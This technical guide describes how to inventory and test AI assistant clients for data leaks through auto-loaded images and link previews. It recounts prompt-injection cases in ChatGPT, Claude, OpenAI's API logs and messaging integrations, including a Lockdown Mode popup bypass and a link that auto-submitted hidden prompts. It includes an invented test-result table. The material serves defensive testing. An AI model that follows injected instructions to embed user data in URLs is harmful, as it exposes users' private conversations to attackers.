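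Some of Rehberger's bypasses still worked when he published Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* in August 2025. By then ChatGPT also had access to recent conversations, which he extracted. OpenAI strengthened url_safe around that time and stopped the attacks he had shown.

OpenAI may also have changed where the check ran. Rehberger noticed in August that url_safe was no longer visible on the client side. Moving the whole check to OpenAI's server would have largely solved the problem of clients that lacked it. But in December 2025, developers on OpenAI's forum still saw url_safe requests in their network traffic while investigating why images that their custom GPTs fetched from outside services had stopped appearing. In *Did something change?*, one of them reported that the same image loaded without a url_safe request when its address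 had not come from the outside service.

So at least some images still went through a visible check at the end of 2025, and where an address came from affected whether ChatGPT requested it. Neither observation shows what the phone and Mac apps did. When OpenAI explained its web index rule in January 2026, it referred to "ChatGPT (and agentic experiences)" and did not list the clients that apply the rule.

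The web app has also continued to load some outside images. In May 2026 the security company Permiso showed that chatgpt.com would fetch images from a page it had just summarised (The Hacker News, 2026). The requests revealed the user's IP address, user agent and referer (a header that identifies the page a request came from), but in the reported attack they did not carry the text of the conversation. This is compatible with OpenAI's rule, which lets a URL load if it was already public.

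In the table, "fixed" means that the client gained a check against images with private data in their addresses. The client may still load outside images, and someone may have found a bypass since.

| Client | First known exposed | First known fixed | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web app | End of March 2023 | December 2023; OpenAI strengthened the check around August 2025 | *ChatGPT Plugins*; Embrace The Red, December 2023; Embrace the Red, 2026 |
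| iOS app | December 2023, version 1.2023.347 (16603) | September 2024; exact date and version unknown | Embrace The Red, December 2023; Embrace The Red, after Black Hat Europe 2024 |
| Android app | Rehberger inferred it in December 2023 and stated it in September 2024; start date and versions unknown | Unknown | Embrace The Red, December 2023; Embrace The Red, September 2024 |
| macOS app | On its release in 2024; first exposed version unknown | September 2024, version 1.2024.247 | Rehberger; Embrace The Red, September 2024 |

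The Android app may well have received the check in the same month as the iPhone app. Testing the current Android app could show whether it is safe now, but not when it became safe.

### Why the prediction came true

Rehberger predicted in December 2023 that each client would need its own fix. The prediction required no inside knowledge, because url_safe checks a URL only when a client requests it.

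The request to url_safe was also easy to leave out by mistake, because an app without it shows every image and produces no error message. A quality tester who confirms that images appear will pass it. The complaints come from people whose app does have the check, like the developers who lost their images in December 2025. If OpenAI's server had withheld each image address until approving it, a Mac app without the necessary code would have shown no outside images, and its developers would probably have noticed before release.

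None of these accounts quotes OpenAI on why the apps lacked the check. Rehberger's warning had been public for months, including in the technology press, before the Mac app appeared. Somebody at OpenAI very likely knew the iPhone app lacked the check and put other work first. The Mac app is harder to judge, because its developers might have postponed the check or never heard of it.

Rehberger warned on Embrace the Red in 2026 that some developers at OpenAI might not know about the new web index rule or adopt it. He called this a typical engineering challenge for a security organisation, and one he had often met. OpenAI already had a recent example. In November 2025, two months before the company published the rule, PromptArmor had reported the same image leak in the screen where developers read their API logs. PromptArmor later described the leak in *OpenAI API Logs*.

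## What counts as a client

A screen counts as a client if it displays an assistant's output. OpenAI's log screen does, but it is not part of any assistant's web, mobile or desktop app, so a tester who checks only those three would miss it. Several other leaks since 2024 have also appeared on screens that a list of those three omits or treats as duplicates. A tester therefore has to find such screens and decide which similar ones need separate tests.

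### The same assistant on a phone

In July 2023, Anthropic stopped Claude's web app from loading images automatically. On 17 December 2024, in an announcement reproduced by Willison (2024), Rehberger said that Anthropic had fixed a data leak he had reported in Claude's iPhone app. He explained that an attacker could have used the leak during a prompt injection attack, and that image leaks often exist in mobile apps too, typically through Markdown.

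The web app had its protection almost 17 months before the iPhone app did. Rehberger gave no reason for the gap. The "Show Image" button was a change to the web app's display code, and the iPhone app probably needed a separate change because it had its own display code. He did not say when the iPhone leak began, so the app may not have been exposed for the whole 17 months. He did not mention Claude's Android app.

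Counting ChatGPT's phone and Mac apps, two vendors had a web fix that did not reach another app. A tester should therefore count the app for each operating system as a separate client, even if the screens look identical. A clean result on an iPhone is weak evidence about Android, because vendors often write the two apps separately.

### Screens for developers and staff

Many companies build their own assistants by connecting their software to OpenAI's models through OpenAI's API (the interface that lets one program use another). OpenAI logs these assistants' conversations, and developers can read the logs on its website.

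PromptArmor demonstrated the log leak with a mock version of a tool that banks use to verify customers' identities. The tool's assistant drew on six sources about a customer, one of which included internet text where an attacker had hidden an instruction. When the user picked one of the suggested questions, the model wrote a Markdown image with the customer's personal data in its URL. A second model flagged and blocked the answer, so the tool never displayed the image and no data leaked there.

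The blocked answer was still in OpenAI's logs. The log viewer displayed answers as Markdown, so when a developer opened the conversation to see why it had been flagged, the developer's browser requested the image, and the attacker's server received the customer's passport details and financial information.

The tool's makers had protected their own screen, but OpenAI's log viewer loaded the image from the same answer. PromptArmor points out that other defences in the tool, such as a CSP, a sanitizer or a plain-text display, would have left the same gap. These defences act on what the tool displays, while the log contains what the model wrote.

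A defence in the app can make the second leak more likely, because developers tend to open flagged conversations. PromptArmor gives another example, in which a sanitizer removed an image from an answer by the AI search service Perplexity. This left an odd, empty reply that a user might well give a thumbs-down. If that feedback sends the conversation to a developer for review, the removed image may load on the developer's screen.

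PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025. OpenAI initially rejected the report but said in January 2026 that a fix was under way. PromptArmor counted five more places with the same weakness. Three were previews in which developers try out a chat, an assistant or an agent they are building. The other two were the ChatKit Playground and the Starter ChatKit app, which help developers build a chat interface. A fuller list in the same article adds a sixth, the Widget Builder.

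The starter app may be the hardest of these to fix, because developers build their own products from copies of it. Those products could lack the same defence, and a fix to OpenAI's original would not automatically reach them.

Ordinary users never see the log viewer, but their data passes through it. One developer may also read the conversations of many customers in a day. The same risk exists wherever staff read formatted conversations, for example in a customer support system or a third-party monitoring dashboard.

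### Messaging apps that carry an assistant

An assistant's maker does not always write the client. In the OpenClaw leak that PromptArmor reported in February 2026, the client was Telegram. The agent could write the same message whether link previews were on or off, but the link leaked data without a click only when they were on.

PromptArmor's public test site, AITextRisk.com, records visits from preview programs and charts the most common ones, including Slack's and Telegram's. Telegram counts as a client even when its own servers fetch the page, because the app displays the assistant's answer.

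PromptArmor's site also lets people report which agent and which messaging app produced a preview, and it uses these reports to show the riskiest combinations. An inventory should likewise count each combination of agent and app as a separate client. OpenClaw in Telegram and OpenClaw in Slack are two clients, and a clean result in one is weak evidence about the other. The OpenClaw setting that turns previews off is part of its Telegram configuration, so changing it may not protect Slack users.

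PromptArmor believes messaging companies should let developers control previews, and agent developers should use that control or pass the choice on to users. It would also like messaging apps to allow different preview settings for individual chats, so people could keep previews on with friends and turn them off with an agent. Testers would then have to record that setting too, since two chats in the same app could behave differently.

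### One flaw in the browser and the desktop app

Two clients can have the same protection, but an attacker can get around it more easily in one than in the other. This happened with ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode. The security company Check Point published a bypass on 5 November 2026, after OpenAI had fixed it.

The bypass used a feature that displays web page code as a live page inside the conversation. Brinsa (2026) notes in *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open* that ChatGPT gained these HTML previews in February 2026, the month OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode. The previews were not on the published list of features the mode restricts. OpenAI had put the preview in a sandbox, a closed-off area whose code cannot reach the rest of the app, and the user had to approve any outside request. But Check Point's Alexey Bukhteyev found that code in the preview could open a popup window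 without approval. The popup's content ran outside the sandbox, and Lockdown Mode's protections did not apply to it, as Duggan (2026) explains in *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup*.

In a browser, the user first had to click inside the preview, because browsers normally block unrequested popups. In ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app built on Electron, the popup opened without a click. According to Brinsa, Check Point made a custom GPT that sent the user's messages to Check Point's server while the user was chatting. A tester who opened the same GPT on the website and clicked nothing could have concluded that Lockdown Mode was working.

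Lockdown Mode was present in both clients, so this was a bypass in both rather than an incomplete rollout. The desktop app lacked the browser's popup blocker, which was neither built by OpenAI nor part of Lockdown Mode. A web app can depend on the browser for some of its safety, and it may lose that protection when a vendor packages the same pages as a desktop app.

The desktop app was safer than a browser against another Check Point attack, which used the popup to imitate a ChatGPT update and deliver malware. Duggan reports that a browser would not block an automatic download, while the desktop app downloaded the file only if the user clicked a link. So a tester can't rank the clients once and then test only the weakest.

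The zero-click result is narrower than some of the coverage suggests. In The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), Check Point's head of research, Eli Smadja, attributes it to "the ChatGPT desktop application". Duggan, who read Check Point's full report, specifies ChatGPT Classic, which Loupia's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* (2026) describes as the old desktop app. The Hacker News also points out that the underlying flaw was not limited to Electron, and the browser version of the attack supports this. But Duggan reports no test of a newer desktop app or of the phone apps, so it is unknown whether they leaked without a click. A client inventory therefore needs a separate entry for each of a vendor's desktop apps.

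OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September by removing the popup permissions from the frame around the preview. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* describes this as a server-side patch, and Duggan writes that users had nothing to install. One change therefore seems to have fixed both the browser and desktop versions.

### How instructions get into a client

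Clients can also differ in how they accept an attacker's instructions. *PromptFiction* (Luz, 2026) describes a flaw that Oasis Security found in Claude Desktop, Anthropic's app for computers. Some links open an app instead of a web page, as a meeting link opens Zoom. A crafted link of this kind opened Claude Desktop and submitted a prompt the attacker had written. The visible part of the prompt could be a harmless request, such as help planning a trip, with malicious instructions hidden below it.

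According to Expert Insights' *Claude Desktop Flaw Let A Single Link Steal Data And Run Code* (2026), a link could fill in the text box in the web version of Claude, but the user still had to press send. In the desktop app, clicking the link also sent the prompt. On a default installation, the prompt could then make Claude collect the user's earlier conversations and send them to an attacker's account. If the user had also given Claude access to their files through a popular extension, the same click could eventually lead to the attacker's code running on the computer.

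A tester who pasted the same hostile text into both clients would have missed this difference, because pasting skips the step where they differed. The inventory therefore has to record how input reaches each client as well as how data can leave it. One client might take input from typed messages, uploaded files and web pages, while another might also accept prompts from links or other apps.

Oasis used a channel from its earlier research on Claude to send the conversations to an account that the attacker controlled, so the attack also did not need an image to carry the data. A test that used an image and a listener could have found no leak in Claude Desktop while this flaw was still open.

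Anthropic fixed the desktop app so that it now sends a prompt from such a link only after the user presses send. Luz advises users to install version 1.1.2321 or later.

One client can also give instructions to another. Claude Dispatch, for example, lets people send work from a phone or browser to Claude Desktop. Weizman found in *ThisBash Escape* that a browser extension with control over claude.ai could use Dispatch to run code through Claude Desktop, even on a different computer, as long as both used the same Claude account. Anthropic is retiring Dispatch, but Weizman names two other features, Claude Code Remote Control and Claude Cowork, that still let a web client direct an agent on a computer.

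If a phone or browser can start work in a desktop app, that connection needs its own entry that records which client sends the instruction and which one carries it out. Typing directly into Claude Desktop does not test this connection.

### Hard cases

Two screens need separate entries if one could leak data while the other does not. That can happen when they use different display code, have different settings or receive the answer by different routes. Some cases are still hard to classify.

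#### Shared chats

A shared chat is a conversation its owner has published through a link. It may look like an ordinary conversation in the web app, but a stranger may have written it and the visitor may not be signed in. In Check Point's malware attack, the victim could open the shared chat without an account. Lockdown Mode is a setting for signed-in users, so a victim without an account could not have turned it on.

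Signed-in visitors face a different risk. In late October 2026, the security company Parameter Labs described how a shared ChatGPT link could let an attacker take over a visitor's account. The Hacker News reported that the hostile code ran as part of chatgpt.com and had access to the visitor's signed-in session. Check Point considers this a separate flaw in the same preview component. Shared chats therefore need their own entry, with one trial signed in and one signed out.

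#### Reopened history

A saved conversation reopens in a client already on the list, so a tester should treat reopening as a second trial in that client, not as a new client. It needs its own trial because the answer may take a different route to the screen, and the saved copy might be the model's original text, as it was in OpenAI's logs.

Testers should also reopen the conversation in the other clients. A user's history is commonly available on all of their devices, so an answer that the web app displayed safely may later appear in the phone app. If the phone app has no protection, it could load the hostile image then, even though the user did everything risky in the web app.

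#### Embedded browser views

An app can combine native screens with web views. ChatGPT's HTML preview is similarly a small web page with its own permissions inside a larger page. An embedded view needs a separate entry if it can load addresses under its own rules.

Web views are hard to recognise, so listing features is easier than listing technical components. A tester can go through the app and note everything that displays or runs material from an answer, such as a code preview, a document editor or a panel of sources. This list would have included the HTML preview, which Lockdown Mode's documentation did not mention.

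#### Old versions

An old version of an app counts as a client as long as people can use it. Randolph Barr, the chief information security officer of Cequence Security, told Expert Insights that automatic updates generally cover individual users of Claude Desktop on macOS and Windows. Companies that manage their own installations should check that they have the patched release.

Few testers can try every version, so a reasonable minimum is the current version and the oldest one that still connects or that the organisation still has on its computers. An app that the vendor has replaced also needs testing if it still works, as Loupia's description of ChatGPT Classic suggests.

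#### Tools on the vendor's servers

ChatGPT can run code in an isolated environment separate from the user's device. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a hidden path from this environment to the public internet. A single malicious prompt could send the user's messages and uploaded files out through it. The user's client did not make the connection, so no check in the apps would have stopped it.

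Such a tool is not a client under the definition, because it doesn't display anything. It still belongs in the inventory under its own heading, since a vendor could fix every app and leave the tool vulnerable. In principle, one set of tests per tool is enough. The client matters only in edge cases, for instance if a phone app offers an older version of the tool, or if the tool requires approval and clients present the request differently.

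### The inventory

A practical way to compile the inventory is to follow one answer to every place where somebody might see it. For example, an employee asks an assistant a question in a browser and later sees the answer again in the history on their phone. The employee shares the conversation with a colleague, who opens the link without signing in. The employee then gives the answer a thumbs-down, and a developer sees it while reviewing the feedback. The answer has now appeared on four screens, but only the employee's browser and phone fit the usual list of web, mobile and desktop.

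Each entry should state the exact version, the operating system, the type of account and any relevant settings, such as link previews or Lockdown Mode. It should also state how instructions can enter and which program is expected to send a request. A client that the tester can't access stays on the list as "not tested". Outside testers will often have to mark a vendor's own staff screens this way.

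The list below is a starting point for any assistant. Few products will have every item.

- The web app, in each browser that its users rely on, on computers and phones.
- The iPhone and iPad app.
- The Android app.
- Every desktop app for macOS and Windows, including a replaced app that still works.
- The oldest version of each installed app that can still connect or that the organisation still uses.
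- Browser sidebars, and assistants inside other products such as office suites and coding apps.
- Features within a client that display or run generated material, such as HTML previews and document editors.
- Shared conversations, opened once while signed in and once while signed out.
- Saved conversations, reopened in the client where they began and in the user's other clients.
- Each pairing of an assistant with a messaging app, with link previews on and off.
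- Developer screens, including API logs, playgrounds and previews of unfinished assistants.
- Products built from a vendor's starter app, which may need a repair of their own.
- Staff screens for support, moderation and monitoring, including those that other companies supply.
- Connections through which one client can start work in another, such as from a phone to a desktop app.
- Tools on the vendor's servers that browse the web or run code, listed separately because they are not clients.

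## How to test every client with a listener

Once the inventory is complete, a tester can display the same kind of answer in every listed client and see which ones contact the listener. Researchers ran similar surveys of e-mail programs in 2018 and messaging apps in 2020, looking for clients that contact outside servers without the user clicking anything. Neither survey involved an AI assistant, but much of their method applies to AI assistants too.

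### Two earlier surveys

The e-mail survey was part of EFAIL, an attack on encrypted e-mail. The attacker alters an encrypted message so that its decrypted text becomes part of an image's address, then sends it to the recipient. The recipient's e-mail program decrypts the message and, if it loads the image, sends the text to the attacker's server. *Efail* (Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues, 2018) tested 48 e-mail programs to find out which would contact an outside server.

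Thirteen clients loaded outside images by default. The others blocked images or asked the user first, but the researchers got past the blocking in 22 clients by trying a long list of less common HTML elements. Products with the same name behaved differently. Outlook 2016 for Windows blocked outside images by default, while Outlook for iPhone, version 2.56.0, loaded them and had no setting to prevent it. Three clients that normally blocked a simple image loaded it when the e-mail was encrypted.

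Poddebniak and colleagues could also test whether decrypted text would leak in 35 of the clients. They tested the two main standards for encrypted e-mail and found leaks in 23 of the 35 clients with S/MIME and in 10 of 28 with OpenPGP. In their draft, they mark ten of the 35 clients as not supporting S/MIME, so 23 of the 25 clients that support it leaked. (The EFAIL website gives 25 of 35, but the rows of the table add up to 23.) A table of results for an assistant should likewise separate clients that blocked an address from clients that lack the feature.

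For the other survey, reported in Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020), Tommy Mysk and Talal Haj Bakry sorted messaging apps by which machine fetches the page behind a link. In ten apps, including Slack, Discord and Zoom, the company's server fetched it. In two others, the receiver's phone did, so anyone who sent a link could learn the receiver's IP address.

Researchers used their own server as the listener and sent a link to a 2.6 GB file on it through Instagram. Several Facebook servers started downloading the file at once, transferring about 24.7 GB in total. Because one link can cause many callbacks, testers should count the distinct test tokens in the log, not the requests.

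The two researchers published the exact iOS and Android version of almost every app they tested. The messaging app LINE passed users' IP addresses to linked sites in version 10.14.0 on iOS and 10.15.2 on Android, and had stopped by versions 10.16.1 and 10.18.0. LINE users could check their own phones against those numbers. An app's behavior also depended on its settings and the user's region. Signal fetched previews only if the user had turned them on, and in February 2021 Facebook switched off previews in Messenger and Instagram for users in Europe.

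In the survey, Mysk considered previews safe if the sender's app fetched the page, because a person who sends a link presumably trusts it. This reasoning doesn't apply to assistants, because an assistant that is following hostile text may send a link that nobody has vetted.

### Testing display separately from obedience

When a test runs the whole attack and the attack fails, it is hard to tell why. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* gives the example of a poisoned document meant to make a research assistant put a malicious link in its report. If no link appears, the search step may not have found the document, a later step may have ranked it too low, or the model may have ignored the instruction. The framework's solution is to insert the hostile text directly after the search step and observe what happens. It compares this to unit testing, in which programmers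 test one component at a time.

For a fix in a client, the best place to insert the text is just before the component under test. A vendor can skip the model and send each client's display code the same prewritten answer containing a test address. Any difference in the result then comes from the clients. If the fix is a filter on the server, the prewritten answer has to enter before the filter. The answer should also arrive in pieces, as a real one does, because SearchLeak worked only while the answer was still streaming.

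Outside testers can't do this, so they have to get the model to write the address. They don't have to trick it, because the display code handles an image address the same way whatever prompted the model to write it. They can upload a document with formatting instructions and openly ask the assistant to follow them.

The wording of a test still affects whether the model leaks the data. *The Framing Gap* tried five versions of one hostile instruction on GPT-4o, and their success rates ranged from 0% to 100%. In another of its experiments, which changed only the label on the secret, the model leaked the secret in all ten trials under one label and in none of 20 under labels that suggested a password or key. An invented launch date is therefore better test data than an invented password.

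The tester then has to confirm that the model wrote the address. Many apps have a copy button that returns the answer as Markdown, and in a browser the developer tools show the text that arrived from the server. If the address is missing, the trial hasn't tested the display code, and the tester should record "no result" instead of a pass. An outside tester can't see whether the model left the address out or the server removed it. But if harmless image addresses come through every time and test addresses never do, a filter on the server is more likely.

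An assistant that browses the web may contact the listener through its browsing tool, which can also confuse the result. Testers should turn browsing off for display tests and test it separately. They should also start with an empty project when testing a coding assistant. *Takedown* (2025), a study of coding agents, found one whose web tool needed no user approval and whose model received the contents of open files by default.

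Obedience needs its own test, but only once for each model. Display needs a test in every client.

### Choosing a test address

Typing an address into the chat and asking for it back is the easiest way to make an assistant write it, but this invalidates the test in ChatGPT. According to Embrace the Red, ChatGPT treats an address in the user's own message as safe for that session. The client may then load the image as OpenAI intends, and the tester may report a leak that doesn't exist.

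The early url_safe service applied this rule broadly. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* describes sending requests directly to the service, which appeared to search everything the user had supplied for a matching string. That included custom instructions, the standing notes that tell ChatGPT how to answer. A test address left in those notes could therefore have affected later trials in new conversations.

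Pasting a whole test document into the chat can cause the same problem, because the pasted text becomes part of the user's message. Claude's page-fetching tool also accepts addresses from user messages, and Willison warns that many applications add untrusted content to those messages. Testers should upload the document as a file or put it on a web page.

Addresses that are already public may also count as safe. OpenAI compares the exact address with its web index, so an address published in a bug report could pass a few months later. Some servers may be exempt from checks. Tenable (2025) found that url_safe always approved addresses on one search engine's domain. The listener should therefore have an ordinary domain of its own.

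Testers can avoid most of these problems by making sure the complete address does not exist anywhere until the model writes it. The uploaded document can contain the first part, and the model can add the invented launch date from the conversation. This test also resembles a real leak more closely than one in which the model copies the address from the user's message.

### Positive controls

If no callback arrives, the client may have blocked the address. The listener may also have been down, the office firewall may have blocked the listener's domain, or the phone may have lost its connection. Testers first run a positive control, a trial that should produce a callback, to rule out these faults.

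In ChatGPT, a tester can type the address of a picture on the listener and ask the assistant to display it, even though such an address is unsuitable for the test itself. A callback shows that this client can load an outside image and that its requests reach the listener.

Other fixes need other controls:

- If the client displays a button in place of the image, as Claude's web app did in 2023, the tester clicks the button.
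- If a Content Security Policy blocks the listener, no address on it will load in the chat. The tester can open a blank page containing the same image in the same browser, and then look in the developer tools for a message that the policy blocked the image in the chat.
- In a messaging app, the tester turns link previews on.
- If the team still has a version of the app that is known to leak, it can run the same test there. This is the most convincing control, because only the app version changes.

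The control should use the same device, network and output form as the test, because a callback from a Markdown image doesn't show that the client can display an HTML image. If the control also fails, the tester can open the control's address in the device's browser. A callback from the browser shows that the connection works, so the client probably doesn't load outside images.

### The procedure

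A security team can follow these steps with its own accounts and invented data.

1. Write down the claim. "The leak is fixed" is too vague to test. A testable version would be: "Since 16 November 2026, no client of this assistant has loaded an outside image whose address contains data from the conversation, unless the user clicked."
2. List the clients from the inventory. Update the version numbers and note the region of each test account.
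3. Prepare a test account that contains nothing real. Turn memory off, so that an instruction from one trial can't affect the next, and clear any custom instructions.
4. Create a new test token for every trial and write it down beforehand. Reusing an address can hide a leak, because browsers keep copies of images they have loaded and may not request them again.
5. Run the positive control. If the listener records nothing, find out why before continuing.
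6. Run a clean trial with the same question and a harmless document. *The Framing Gap* counted a leak only if the hostile page leaked the secret and a matching clean page did not.
7. Run the test. Scroll until the place where the image belongs is on the screen, since some apps load images only when they come into view. Don't click anything in the answer.
8. Wait for a fixed time, such as ten minutes. Choose it before the test, and make it much longer than the slowest callback in the controls.
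9. Save a screenshot, the raw text of the answer and the matching log line, or a note that there was none. The screenshot is not enough. In 480 runs by Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), a hostile web page made an agent send out private data about 89% of the time, even when the answer on the screen looked harmless.
10. Repeat the test after each release of a client. A change to the model or the server can also make old results obsolete, and outsiders may not hear about it, so a monthly run is sensible even if no app has changed.

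The number of trials for each combination depends mainly on how reliably the model writes the address.

### A worked example

Suppose a team wants to check the claim in step 1 for an assistant with five clients: a web app and apps for iPhone, Android, Mac and Windows. In each client, the team tests three output forms: a Markdown image, an HTML image and a plain link.

Real attacks have used different image notations. SearchLeak used an HTML image, while EchoLeak used a style of Markdown that puts the address on a separate line, according to trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*. The plain link is for detecting previews, so the tester doesn't click it. Tenable found that ChatGPT's url_safe also checked ordinary links, so clicking the link there may bring up a warning.

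The team tests each form in a new chat and in a reopened one. Five clients, three forms and two states make 30 combinations, or cells. With a ten-minute wait for each cell, one tester doing them in order would spend five hours waiting. Several people can test at once because the tokens distinguish their callbacks.

A client that has already displayed the image may have kept a copy and make no new request when it reopens the chat. The team therefore creates the conversation in a client that has just passed the test for a new chat, then opens it in the client under test. For the web app, the team uses a second browser.

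These are the invented results. Every client passed a positive control with a Markdown image.

| Client | Markdown image, new | Markdown image, reopened | HTML image, new | HTML image, reopened | Plain link, new | Plain link, reopened |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web app in Firefox 150 | None | None | None | None | None | None |
| iPhone app 5.2.0 | None | Callback | None | None | None | None |
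| Android app 5.1.3 | Callback | Callback | Shown as text | Shown as text | None | None |
| Mac app 3.4.0 | None | None | Callback | Callback | None | None |
| Windows app 3.4.0 | None | None | No result | Callback | None | None |

"None" means the answer contained the address but the listener received no request. The web app has six such results, so a team that tested only the web app would have confirmed the vendor's claim. The other four clients produced six callbacks in total.

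The Android app loaded the Markdown image in both states, which suggests that version 5.1.3 lacks the fix. It displayed the HTML tag as plain text, so those two cells are not evidence of whether the fix is present. They could change if a later version renders HTML.

In the iPhone app, the fix worked for a new answer but not for a saved one. The app probably checks answers as they arrive but not when it loads them from the history. The tester should repeat the test in this cell with a conversation created on the iPhone, in case the app treats conversations from other clients differently.

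The Mac app blocked Markdown images but loaded HTML images, so it probably has a check that doesn't recognise the HTML notation. In the Windows app, the model declined to write the HTML image in the new chat, so that cell has no result. The callback from the reopened chat suggests that a new chat would leak too, so the team should try again with different wording.

No link caused a callback, so there is no sign of automatic previews in these five apps.

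### Automating the tests

A vendor can automate most of this work, which is tedious to do by hand for every release. Software companies use a build system, which assembles an app from its source code and runs tests on it whenever a developer makes a change. A vendor can add a display test that gives the display code a set of stored answers, records every address the code tries to load, and fails if any address is forbidden. The test doesn't need a model or an internet connection, so it can run in seconds.

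The stored answers should cover more than the three forms in the example. Poddebniak and colleagues drew some of their e-mail tests from HTTPLeaks, a public collection of HTML elements that cause a browser to send requests. At least one stored answer should contain an image that the client is supposed to load, because if no request for it appears, the test itself is broken.

A test inside the app can miss requests from other components, such as a preview that the operating system fetches. To catch those, the team needs to run the complete app with a listener. Software can open a prepared conversation in the app on an emulator, which is a simulated phone, take a screenshot and search the listener's log for the token. Emulators often run special test builds, so the team should also test the app store version on a few real phones.

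Ready-made tools can create the addresses. *Web Injection*, a page in the security company Mend's documentation, describes a service that prepares a web resource for a test and returns a unique address for it. The tool then gives that address to the assistant, so a request for it shows only that the assistant opened a page it was given. A test of the fix also requires the model to build another address from what it finds on that page.

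A release gate is a rule in the build system that stops a release until certain tests have passed. The gate has to count a missing test as a failure. Otherwise a new app will pass if its developers didn't know about the URL check and so never wrote a test for it. The gate should also block any client that isn't in the inventory.

Such a gate would probably have blocked the ChatGPT Mac app in 2024, because the app's display code would have loaded the forbidden image. But a gate can't detect server changes made between releases, so the vendor should also run the tests on released versions every night.

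### What model-only scanners miss

Some scanners that appear to automate this work test only the model. A well-known one is garak, an open-source program that sends hostile prompts to a language model and grades the replies. Its Markdown tests check whether these prompts can make the model write an image or link with private data in the address.

garak grades replies largely by matching text patterns. The basic pattern matches a Markdown image whose URL has a full server name, a file name and a query string with something after the equals sign. garak doesn't display the reply in a client or run a listener to catch requests, so it would give the same grade whether or not an app has url_safe.

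The patterns also miss some addresses that a client would load. They cover several kinds of Markdown but no HTML image tags. For Markdown images, they allow only letters and digits in the file name, so the hyphen in `web-7f3k9q.png`, the file name in the sample log line, would prevent a match.

Garak's results describe a model's behavior and don't show whether an app built on it leaks data. AVID (2026), a public database of AI vulnerabilities, records that OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b passed all 256 attempts in one of garak's image tests, but a chat app built on that model could still load any outside image. In a March 2026 entry, AVID reports that Google's gemma-3n-E4B-it passed 187 of 256 attempts (73%) in the link test, but an app that blocks unknown addresses could use that model without leaking data through them. Garak is useful for the obedience test, which measures how often a model writes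 such addresses.

Promptfoo's *Data Exfiltration Plugin* comes closer to a listener test. It creates hostile web pages, asks an agent to read them and uses a server to record whether the agent contacts forbidden addresses. It requires an agent that can browse the web, so it mainly tests the agent's tools. To test a phone app's display code, someone would still have to open the answer in that app.

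If the plugin loses track of a page, it uses a model to grade the agent's reply instead. The documentation warns that "unavailable tracking is not evidence that the agent is secure". Similarly, if a tester's positive control has failed, a listener that records no requests is not evidence that the client is secure.

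## What a callback proves and what silence proves

A callback with a fresh test token in the listener's log shows that something loaded the test address, since nobody could have guessed the token. The tester can conclude that the client lacks the fix only if they also know that the client sent the request and that the fix should have blocked this address.

Programs other than the client under test also request addresses, including preview bots and the servers behind an assistant's browsing tool. In Cyber Advisors' *Burp Service Fingerprinting Through External Interaction* (2019), the tester's router passed unknown addresses to the security company Trend Micro, whose servers then visited them. *Yesterday Once More*, a study in ACM's *IMC '24* (2024), found networks that stored data from traffic passing through them, sometimes for over 10 days, and used it to send their own requests. A request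 that arrives within seconds of the test, from the IP address of the device under test, most likely came from that device.

### Addresses that a fix lets through

It is harder to know whether a fix should have blocked an address when the vendor hasn't published its rule. When Rehberger discovered url_safe in ChatGPT's web app in December 2023, he tried 36 image addresses on his own server, one for each letter and digit. Nine loaded, according to Embrace The Red. The service approved `a.png` and rejected `d.png`, although both were in the same folder, and he could not tell why.

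All nine callbacks came from a client that had the fix, so someone who tried only `a.png` could have wrongly reported that the check was missing.

A better test uses an address that a client with the fix has just blocked. Suppose the web app leaves out an image and the listener records nothing. The tester then gets the assistant to write the same address in the iPhone app, with the same account and uploaded document. Since the web app never requested the address, the token is still unused, and a callback now points to the iPhone app, which either lacks the check or ignores its result.

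Testing several different addresses can also show whether an app has the check. If the check approves a quarter of all addresses, as url_safe did in Rehberger's test, the chance that it approves four in a row is 0.25⁴, or about 0.4%. An app without the check would load all four. This calculation assumes the four verdicts are independent, which is a guess as long as the rule is secret.

Seeing the request to url_safe and its reply in the browser's developer tools is stronger evidence that the web app has the check than any pattern of callbacks.

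### How callbacks performed in *Silent Egress*

Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured how well callbacks reveal leaks. They ran the whole experiment on their own machines. A small open-weight model, qwen2.5:7b, controlled an agent that automatically previewed web addresses. One server supplied hostile pages and another listened for callbacks. The user's message was always a request to summarise the page.

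The researchers varied where on the page the hostile instruction appeared, whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it sent the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The listener recorded a request in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%, though the paper's abstract gives the probability as about 0.89. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless, so a check that read only the answer would have missed them. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the listener. That result alone is consistent with a false callback rate of up to about 2.5%, but the true rate is presumably much lower because the harmless pages contained no attack instructions.

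The 0.89 is the average callback rate for an agent that made its requests with a web tool, not for chat apps, and no client had to display an image. The setup also favoured the attacker, since the secret was visible to the model and the system prompt contained little besides the format for using tools. The agent contacted the listener in at least 97% of runs when it sent the secret whole, but in only 60% to 90% when it had to split it.

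Lan and colleagues also tested defences, with 30 runs for each. When they added warnings to the model's instructions and marked web content as untrusted, the callback rate fell from 100% to 57%. A tester who ran a single trial against that agent would have had a 43% chance of seeing no callback, even though the route to the listener was still open.

Two of the other defences produced an empty log for different reasons. With a list of permitted domains, the agent tried to send the secret in all 30 runs and the list blocked every attempt. With a filter for random-looking strings, the agent never tried to send it, so those runs don't show whether the filter can block a request.

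### Other explanations for silence

Before treating silence as a sign of a fix, a tester has to exclude at least five other explanations.

| Explanation | Check that excludes it |
|---|---|
| The model refused to write the address or altered it | Read the raw answer and compare the address with the intended one, character by character |
| The client or a server already had a copy of the image | Use a new token in every trial |
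| The network blocked the listener | Load a control address from the same device and network just before and after the trial |
| The account or device was in a group that already had the fix | Repeat the test with other accounts and app versions, and ask the vendor whether the rollout is complete |
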